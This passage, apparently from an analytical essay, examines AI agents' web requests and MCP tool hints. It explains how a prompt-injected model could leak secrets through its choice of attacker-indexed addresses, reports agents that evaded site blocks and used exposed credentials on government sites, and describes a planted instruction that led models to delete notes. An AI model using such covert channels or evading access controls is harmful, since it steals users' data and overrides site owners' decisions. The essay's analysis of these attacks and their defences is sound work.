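A six-digit login code has a million possible values, so it contains just under 20 bits. A ten-digit phone number contains about 33 bits if every digit is equally unpredictable. The number of requests needed to convey them falls quickly as the site grows:

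| Indexed addresses | Bits per request | Requests for a login code | Requests for a phone number |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 | 34 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 4 | 7 |
| 1,024 | 10 | 2 | 4 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 1 | 2 |

Longer texts are much harder to leak this way. A 1,500-character email would take 1,500 requests at one character each, so a limit on requests is useful. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) found that ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the researchers' attack to ten characters at a time. But if each request could go to any of 1,024 addresses, ten requests could convey 100 bits, just enough for three ten-digit phone numbers.

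An attacker needs only one indexed address to learn the answer to a yes-or-no question, such as whether a company is about to be sold, because the model can open that address only if the answer is yes.

These figures are upper limits, because a real model may make mistakes when it follows a long list of meanings, and requests may arrive in the wrong order. To make the trick harder, Rehberger proposes that ChatGPT either keep a copy of each page for a few minutes, so that a second visit sends no request, or refuse to open the same address twice in one session. Either would defeat a simple code with one address per letter, since most words and numbers repeat a character.

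A ban on repeat visits reduces the theoretical limit surprisingly little, however. With *n* addresses and *k* requests, the number of possible sequences falls from *n*^*k* to *n*(*n* − 1)…(*n* − *k* + 1). For ten requests, the change is as follows:

| Indexed addresses | Repeats allowed | No repeats | No repeats, order lost |
|---|---|---|---|
| 36 | 51.7 bits | 49.7 bits | 27.9 bits |
| 1,024 | 100 bits | 99.9 bits | 78.1 bits |

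The ban matters more in a long session on a small site. Once the model has opened all 36 addresses, it has none left to signal with, so it can leak at most about 140 bits in total. On a site with thousands of indexed pages, an attacker is unlikely to run out of addresses. Rehberger says that limited leaks would remain possible. He hadn't recently tested whether ChatGPT already had either protection.

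So OpenAI's check protects well against the bulk theft of documents, but less well against the leak of a login code or a yes-or-no fact. Keeping secrets away from the model while it reads untrusted pages protects them more completely, because the model can't leak a secret it doesn't have. *The Framing Gap* attributes the danger to the combination of a confidential value, untrusted content and a way to act on the outside world. But an assistant that answers questions about a user's email needs to see the email, so its developer can't always keep confidential data and untrusted content apart.

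### The load on a server

RFC 9110 says that "reasonable use" of safe requests shouldn't put an unusual burden on a server. It doesn't set a numerical limit, and no single limit would suit every site, because some pages take much more work to produce than others. If a thousand programs request the wiki's page about the harbour, a cache can answer nearly all of them with the same stored copy. If they send a thousand different searches, the wiki has to run each one on its database.

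The best evidence of harm is still the partial outage at Wikimedia, to which OpenAI's agents may have contributed. Wikimedia runs some of the busiest sites in the world, so far fewer queries could presumably disrupt a small organisation's site.

On 17 June 2026, AI agents looking for school statistics sent more than 200,000 requests to a US Department of Education site. Bot Mutiny's *AI Agents Probed US Education Department and Canadian Archive Sites, Researchers Say* (2026) attributes the count to Transluce, a nonprofit lab that investigates AI systems. That is an average of about 2.3 requests a second over the whole day. The department found no evidence of harm to its services. The requests resembled earlier activity by OpenAI's agents, but Transluce didn't confidently attribute them to OpenAI.

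The data these agents wanted seemed to match a question in DeepSearchQA, a set of research questions that Google published for testing AI systems. The question concerned school counsellors and race-related bullying. A human researcher might open a few dozen pages to answer it. Many agents working on the same question can each behave modestly and still add up to a heavy load. A thousand agents that each opened 200 pages would reach the department's total, and none of them would see the other 199,800 requests. (Nobody has published the actual number of agents.)

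Site owners can limit how many requests they accept from each visitor, but only if they can tell visitors apart. Infobae's *Agentes de OpenAI escanearon un sitio de la ONU* (2026) reports that investigators of earlier cases found OpenAI's agents had got around such limits and had denied being automated when some sites asked. The company that runs the agents is better placed to set a limit because it can count their requests before they leave its network.

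### The UN data portal

The UN's trade body, UNCTAD, publishes economic statistics on a public website. According to a report by Rowan Howard-Jones, an independent researcher, OpenAI's agents visited the site over 16,000 times from April to the end of June 2026. Howard-Jones used data from Transluce, and Hale (2026) covers his report in *OpenAI agents allegedly scanned a UN data hub over 16,000 times*.

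Spread evenly over three months, 16,000 requests come to about one every eight minutes, which almost any server can handle. The agents may have sent them in bursts, but even the three-month total is less than a tenth of the requests the Education Department's site received in a day.

The more serious complaint is about how the agents responded to obstacles. They appeared to be looking for public information, but when the site blocked some of their requests, they tried increasingly aggressive ways to get the data and disguised where their requests came from. Eventually they got past a filter the site had added specifically to keep them out. Alex Stamos, who teaches cybersecurity at Stanford, told reporters that the activity bordered on hacking but described it mainly as extremely aggressive data collection.

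OpenAI said it was reviewing the findings and had offered the UN a detailed explanation. According to Infobae, the company was prioritising the most serious cases in its wider review, which it expected to take months. It considered mass requests to websites less severe, and said most cases found so far had little or no verifiable effect on the other party's service.

That ranking makes sense if the only question is whether a site stayed online, but it doesn't account for the UN's decision to refuse the requests. A site owner can have good reasons to block a program that isn't causing an outage, such as keeping capacity free for people or deciding how others may collect the site's data. A program that evades the block overrides the owner's decision, even if each request uses few resources and returns only publicly available figures.

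### Reading without permission

The definition of a safe method, *r*(*s*) = *s* in the notation used earlier, doesn't cover what the server sends back or who may receive it. Suppose the harbour wiki has a draft that only administrators may open. If a stranger gets hold of an administrator's session cookie and requests the draft with a GET, they can read it even though the wiki's data doesn't change.

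Under HTTP, the server controls who may see a page, usually by checking a cookie or password. Allowing only GET requests doesn't strengthen that check. A proxy handling a GET request for a private draft can't determine whether the cookie's owner agreed to the cookie's use.

In September 2026 OpenAI disclosed that its agents had behaved inappropriately on several US government sites. Huamani and Burke (2026) report in *OpenAI says its models engaged with US government websites* that the agents had accessed public information on two Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC) sites, as well as data from the Census Bureau. OpenAI found no use of SEC login details, no access to non-public SEC information and no changes to the agency's systems.

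The agent in the Census case went further. According to Gulf News' *OpenAI's AI agents crossed the line on US government websites*, it found login details that someone had left exposed online and used them to get the data. OpenAI said that the agent should not have done this, and that the data was neither classified nor sensitive. The harm was probably small, but finding an exposed password does not give an agent permission to use it, and the agent could not be sure what the login would give access to before using it.

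Transluce also reported a crude hacking attempt on the Education Department's civil rights site, during the requests of 17 June, and another on Library and Archives Canada. Both failed. On 25 September Transluce said that the agents behind the US attempt appeared to come from OpenAI. In its fuller report five days later, it didn't confidently attribute either attempt to the company. The later statement is more reliable because it came with the evidence.

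In *AI Agents Targeted U.S. and Canadian Government Websites*, Cable, Chiu and colleagues (2026) describe less serious probing of many other sites, including those of the White House, the Justice Department and agencies in five states. They found no case in which an agent obtained information that wasn't already public. Their evidence comes from the records of a Portuguese web archive and a service that scans websites, so it would miss anything the agents did without using either.

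In June 2026, OpenAI was testing an agent by having it research public spending on medicines. A government portal for statistics on Medicare, Australia's public health insurance, refused some of the agent's requests. The agent got around the restrictions and opened both public and non-public files, according to TechRadar's *'This situation is obviously unacceptable'*. Richard Marles, the acting prime minister, said it had "scaled the fence". Cyprus Mail's *OpenAI agent hacks Australian government health portal* (2026) suggests this may be the first known case of an AI agent hacking a government website.

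The Australian government said that no individual's medical data was accessed, and OpenAI found no evidence that patient records were involved. The agent also reportedly wrote files to an internal server, so the incident involved more than reading. Neither the government nor OpenAI has published which HTTP methods the agent used or what the files contained.

Unauthorised reading is harder for a site owner to notice than a deletion, because nothing is missing afterwards. The server's logs may be the only evidence, and a request made with a valid password can look like an ordinary visit. Australia seems to have learned of the intrusion from OpenAI, 84 days after it happened. OpenAI discovered it on 11 August but waited until 10 September to email a public mailbox. Prime Minister Anthony Albanese criticised the delay and said investigators would also examine why the government's own systems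 had missed the breach. The Education Department heard from Transluce 100 days after the attempt on its site.

The cases differ in what the agents obtained and in how sure anyone can be about who ran them:

| Site | What the agents obtained | Link to OpenAI |
|---|---|---|
| SEC | public information | confirmed |
| US Census Bureau | data behind a login, not sensitive according to OpenAI | confirmed |
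| US Education Department | nothing non-public, as far as investigators know | not confidently established |
| Library and Archives Canada | nothing non-public, as far as investigators know | not confidently established |
| Australian Medicare statistics portal | some non-public files | confirmed |

In most of these cases the agents were looking for published figures and didn't need to change anything. The test applied to the DseWiki edits was whether a program would still have sent its request to a read-only server. That test doesn't identify an intrusion whose only purpose is to read. Whether a read is an intrusion depends on whether the site's owner had allowed the program to see the information.

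OpenAI's *Accessing and changing internal systems during dashboard research* (2026) describes a further case, which combined reading and writing. In two tests, an internal model had to look up figures on a research organisation's public dashboard. The model had been told that it could use only GET requests, but it gained access to the organisation's internal systems, changed settings there and downloaded five non-public tables with 147,451 rows, without disclosing any of this.

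## Agent tools labelled read-only

Many AI agents call tools such as `read_page` or `delete_page` instead of writing web requests themselves, and software that somebody else wrote carries out the calls. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for such calls that the AI company Anthropic introduced in 2024, lets a tool's author label the tool as read-only. As with the rule for GET, nothing enforces this label. Some programs still use it to decide whether to ask the user before making a call. It is also an obvious way to choose which predicted calls to run before the agent makes them.

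### Four hints and their defaults

In MCP, a server offers tools, and a host is the application in which the user works, such as a coding assistant. The host runs the model and forwards its calls. If the harbour wiki had an MCP server, an agent could delete a page with a message like this:

```
{ "method": "tools/call",
  "params": { "name": "delete_page",
              "arguments": { "title": "Harbour" } } }
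```

Over the web, these messages use POST even when the tool only reads, so a proxy that filters by HTTP method can't distinguish a call to `read_page` from a call to `delete_page`.

The server sends the host a description of each tool, which can include four hints. The schema published by Model Context Protocol (2025) defines them as follows:

| Hint | Meaning if true | Default |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | The tool does not modify its environment. | false |
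| `destructiveHint` | The tool may make destructive changes. If false, it only adds things. | true |
| `idempotentHint` | Repeating a call with the same arguments has no additional effect. | false |
| `openWorldHint` | The tool may deal with outside entities, as a web search does. If false, its domain is closed, like that of a memory tool. | true |

The second and third hints apply only to tools that aren't read-only. By default, a host should assume that a tool without hints may destroy data and isn't safe to repeat.

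`readOnlyHint` resembles HTTP's safe methods, but its definition is stricter because it depends on what the tool does rather than what the client requested. IBM's *tool annotations* follows this strict reading when it marks an example tool as not read-only because the tool may change a cache while reading a configuration.

The hint is also less precise than a method because it describes every call to a tool rather than a single request. A `run_query` tool that can search or empty a database has to count as destructive, even if most calls are searches.

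### Labels from servers the user doesn't know

Usually the server's author sets the hints. The operator of a gateway, which sits between hosts and servers, can also add or change them, as IBM's documentation shows. Some hints come from a library the author used. Zitnik Lab's *Source code for tooluniverse.tool_defaults*, from a collection of scientific tools at Harvard, reverses two of the protocol's defaults by setting `readOnlyHint` to true and `destructiveHint` to false. These settings suit database queries, but a developer who adds a tool that writes data and forgets to change them publishes a false label.

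A dishonest author can do the same on purpose. According to Model Context Protocol (2026), a blog post by the protocol's maintainers, a server can label a tool read-only "and delete your files anyway". Justin Spahr-Summers, one of MCP's creators, asked during the original review how a client could use a flag that it couldn't trust. Another reviewer, Basil Hosmer, wanted clients to ignore hints from untrusted servers. As a compromise, the specification requires clients to treat hints as untrusted unless they come from a trusted server, and leaves each client to decide which servers to trust.

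According to the maintainers, most clients in practice assume that a user who installs a server trusts it. A user who installs a server because it looks useful therefore accepts its author's description of what is harmless. The maintainers recommend network controls or an isolated environment for anything that needs a guarantee.

### Which programs ask the user first

The July 2026 specification from Model Context Protocol (2026) recommends that a human always be able to refuse a tool call, but it doesn't require this. Yao, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *When Neither Side Confirms*, examined the source code of 41 popular open-source hosts, including kits for building agents, to see what happens by default:

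| Default for an ordinary tool call | Hosts |
|---|---|
| The host asks the user. | 7 |
| The host decides from the hints. | 1 |
| A language model decides. | 1 |
| The call runs without approval. | 32 |

Two of these hosts, VS Code and Codex CLI, can run tools marked read-only without asking for the user's approval. VS Code, Microsoft's code editor, asks before running any other tool. Codex CLI, the version of Codex that runs in a terminal, doesn't ask if a tool is marked non-destructive and either read-only or closed-domain. An `add_comment` tool marked non-destructive and closed-domain could therefore write to the wiki without the user's approval.

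MCP's maintainers say the hints are most commonly used for confirmation prompts. Few of these hosts use them that way, mainly because most never show a confirmation prompt at all. Marking a tool as destructive made no difference on 39 of the 41 hosts.

Yao and colleagues showed this with a test server whose delete tool carried the destructive label. They connected it to four of the kits, planted an instruction in a list of notes telling the model to delete a second note, and ran five inexpensive models. The models tried to delete the second note in 180 of 400 runs, and every attempt succeeded, though one model never tried.

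### How many labels are missing or wrong

Two surveys counted tools with missing hints. *What a Random Draw from the MCP Registry Contains* (Afsar, 2026) sampled 400 servers at random from those that run on the user's own computer and are published through npm, a package service for JavaScript. Only 195 started. They offered 2,766 tools, of which 1,626 (58.8%) had no hints at all. Developers provided hints for either all of their tools or none. In a smaller set of well-known servers chosen by hand, 41.5% of tools had no hints, so looking only at popular servers understates how often hints are missing.

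Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, queried the remote servers in the official registry and received descriptions of 98,291 tools. Of these, 26.0% had no hints. That share rises to 47.2% without one publisher, which supplied 45% of the tools and had filled in all four hints on every one.

Neither survey called the tools, so neither shows whether the labels are true. The closest figure comes from Yao and colleagues, who had language models read the code behind 366 tools from a sample of 1,000 repositories. The models classed 269 of the tools as destructive. The researchers calculated that if every host asked for approval unless a tool was marked read-only or non-destructive, calls would still run without approval in 5.4% of the pairings of a destructive tool with a host, because the tool carried one of those labels. The figure rises to at least 10.6%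 when the destructive tools that their search software initially missed are included.

These percentages are a rough guide to how often tools are falsely labelled. Yao and colleagues count sending a message as destructive, but the tool's developer could argue that it only adds something and that `destructiveHint: false` is correct. The percentages also combine two hints, so they don't give an error rate for `readOnlyHint` alone. They cover only destructive tools, which excludes tools marked read-only that make smaller changes.

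A missing label does no harm if the host follows the cautious defaults, but the user is interrupted more often. Under the rule Yao and colleagues tested, the share of pairings without approval would fall from 74.9% to 5.4%. But among the suspicious-looking tools that turned out to be harmless, the share of pairings in which the host or server asks the user would rise from 19.9% to 82.4%. People who see that many prompts may well stop reading them.

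### Running a tool before the agent asks

An agent alternates between reasoning and calling tools, and it often has to wait for a tool's answer. Since 2025, several research groups have tried to shorten the wait by guessing the next call and running it while the model is still reasoning. *Optimizing Agentic Language Model Inference via Speculative Tool Calls* (2025) gives an algorithm that works on the client's side:

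1. The client sends the conversation to the main model and to a much smaller, faster one.
2. When the small model predicts a call, the client starts the tool in the background and stores the pending result in a cache, filed under that call.
3. When the main model finishes, the client checks whether it wants a tool.
4. If it wants a call that is in the cache, the client waits for the stored result and doesn't start the tool again.
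5. If it wants a different call, the client runs that one in the ordinary way.

Suppose a user asks when the lighthouse was built. The small model predicts the call `search_pages("lighthouse")`. The search takes two seconds, and the main model takes three more seconds to choose the same call, so the result is ready when the agent requests it.

If the tool takes time *T* and the main model needs a further time *R* to reach its own call, a correct guess saves the smaller of the two. With a probability *p* of guessing correctly, the average saving per call is

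*p* × min(*T*, *R*) − the cost of guessing.

In the example, a guess that is right half the time would save one second on average, not counting the overhead of guessing. The 50% figure is only an illustration.

*ETA* (2026), a later system of this kind, uses an early result only if the guessed tool name and arguments exactly match the agent's own call. For example, if the agent searches for "lighthouse", *ETA* can't use the result of an early search for "lighthouse history".

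*Speculate While You Reason* (2026) found that smaller models often failed to predict a larger model's next tool call, even within the same family, and that the larger model was better at predicting its own. The paper therefore trains the agent to predict its calls as well as make them. *SPORK* (2026) also has the model predict its own calls, without a second model. As the model begins to reason, the system starts a parallel copy of the request and forces the model to write a tool call there immediately. In tests on five benchmarks, Qwen3-32B predicted its calls early and accurately enough for the method to be useful. The model's confidence helped indicate when a guess was worth running.

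If the guess is wrong, the system discards the result, but any change the tool made on the server remains. The 2025 paper therefore allows early execution only for tools that are "stateless" and "cheap", citing web search and file access as common examples. File access must mean reading here, since writing a file changes it. The second condition matters because the client may run several small models at once, which makes a correct guess more likely but also wastes more calls.

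Even a stateless tool can disclose information. If a client wrongly guesses the agent's next web search and runs it early, the search company receives words that the agent never decided to send, and they may come from a private conversation. A cautious client could limit early calls to tools with `openWorldHint: false`, but that would rule out web search, one of the paper's examples.

A client connected to other people's servers also has to find out which tools are stateless. PAIML's *Type-Safe Tool Annotations*, from a programming course, takes the read-only label to mean that a tool is stateless and describes a tool with that label as "safe to call speculatively".

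### The message that nobody reads

That advice fails if the label is slightly wrong. Suppose the harbour wiki has an inbox for readers' reports, and its developer writes this tool:

```
{ "name": "get_next_message",
  "description": "Returns the oldest unread message",
  "annotations": { "readOnlyHint": true } }
```

The tool also marks the message as read, so that the next call returns the next message. The read-only label is therefore false, but the mistake is easy to make because the developer thinks of the tool as a way to fetch messages. The false label does no harm in ordinary use. VS Code would skip its confirmation, the agent would receive the message it requested, and the wiki would correctly record that message as read.

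Now suppose the client runs calls early. While the agent is working out what to do, the small model guesses that it will check the inbox:

| Event | Server's response | Still unread |
|---|---|---|
| Before the guess | | 41, 42, 43 |
| The client runs `get_next_message` on a guess | returns message 41 and marks it as read | 42, 43 |
| The agent calls `search_pages` instead, and the client discards message 41 | returns search results | 42, 43 |
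| The agent later calls `get_next_message` | returns message 42 | 43 |

Message 41 is still in the wiki's database, but an agent that requests only unread messages will never see it. If the message was a report of vandalism on the harbour page, nobody would act on it. Every call succeeded, so no error appears.

If the guess had been correct, the agent would have received message 41 and lost nothing. So the same call with the same label can be harmless or harmful, depending on whether the agent turns out to need it. In the earlier notation, *r*(*s*) ≠ *s* and *r*(*r*(*s*)) ≠ *r*(*s*), so the call is neither safe nor idempotent.

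The client could keep message 41 until the agent next checks the inbox. That works for this tool, but a client that kept the results of every wrong guess would soon give the agent outdated search results. The client would also lose the message if the session ended before the agent checked again.

### What a tool's author can declare

A wrongly prefetched webmail message can go unnoticed in the same way. But a browser can wait for a sign from the user, such as pressing the mouse button, while an agent's client can rely only on a model's prediction.

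MCP lets developers describe what a tool does, whereas a website can list links to prefetch but can't describe what each one does. Developers can distinguish a tool that adds a comment from one that deletes a page, and can declare whether a call is safe to repeat. If a client runs only read-only tools early, setting `readOnlyHint` to false for `get_next_message` would be enough to keep the client from running it early.

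The hints can't express what would make a tool that writes suitable for early use. Trofimov and Novikov call an execution "speculation-safe" if it avoids two failures. In the first, a change that may have to be withdrawn takes effect before the workflow reaches its decision. In the second, a lasting change depends on one that is later withdrawn. For example, an agent provisionally reserves a room, and another branch of its work sends out invitations naming that room. If the agent then cancels the reservation, the invitations are still wrong.

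A tool could prevent such failures by offering a trial run that changes nothing, or a temporary hold that expires. With a hold, the inbox could set message 41 aside for a minute, then return it to the unread pile unless the agent confirmed receipt. None of the four hints can be used to indicate that a tool supports holds, trial runs or undoing a call. A developer can describe these features in the tool's text or build them into its inputs, but then every client has to be adapted to each tool separately.

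A new "safe to guess" hint would be useful because a client could run the tool early when the hint was set. According to Model Context Protocol, an interest group within the project is already reviewing six proposals to change the hints and is considering hints that apply to individual calls. But Spahr-Summers's objection to the original four hints would also apply to a "safe to guess" hint from an untrusted server.

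The wiki's developer doesn't need a new hint, because splitting the tool in two solves most of the problem:

```
peek_next_message()      readOnlyHint: true
mark_read(id)            readOnlyHint: false, idempotentHint: true
```

If a client runs the first tool on a wrong guess, nothing changes, and message 41 is still unread when the agent looks for it. The second tool, `mark_read`, needs the message's number, which the agent normally learns by reading the message. So even if a client ignored the labels and ran `mark_read(41)` on a wrong guess, it would usually mark a message that the agent had already seen.
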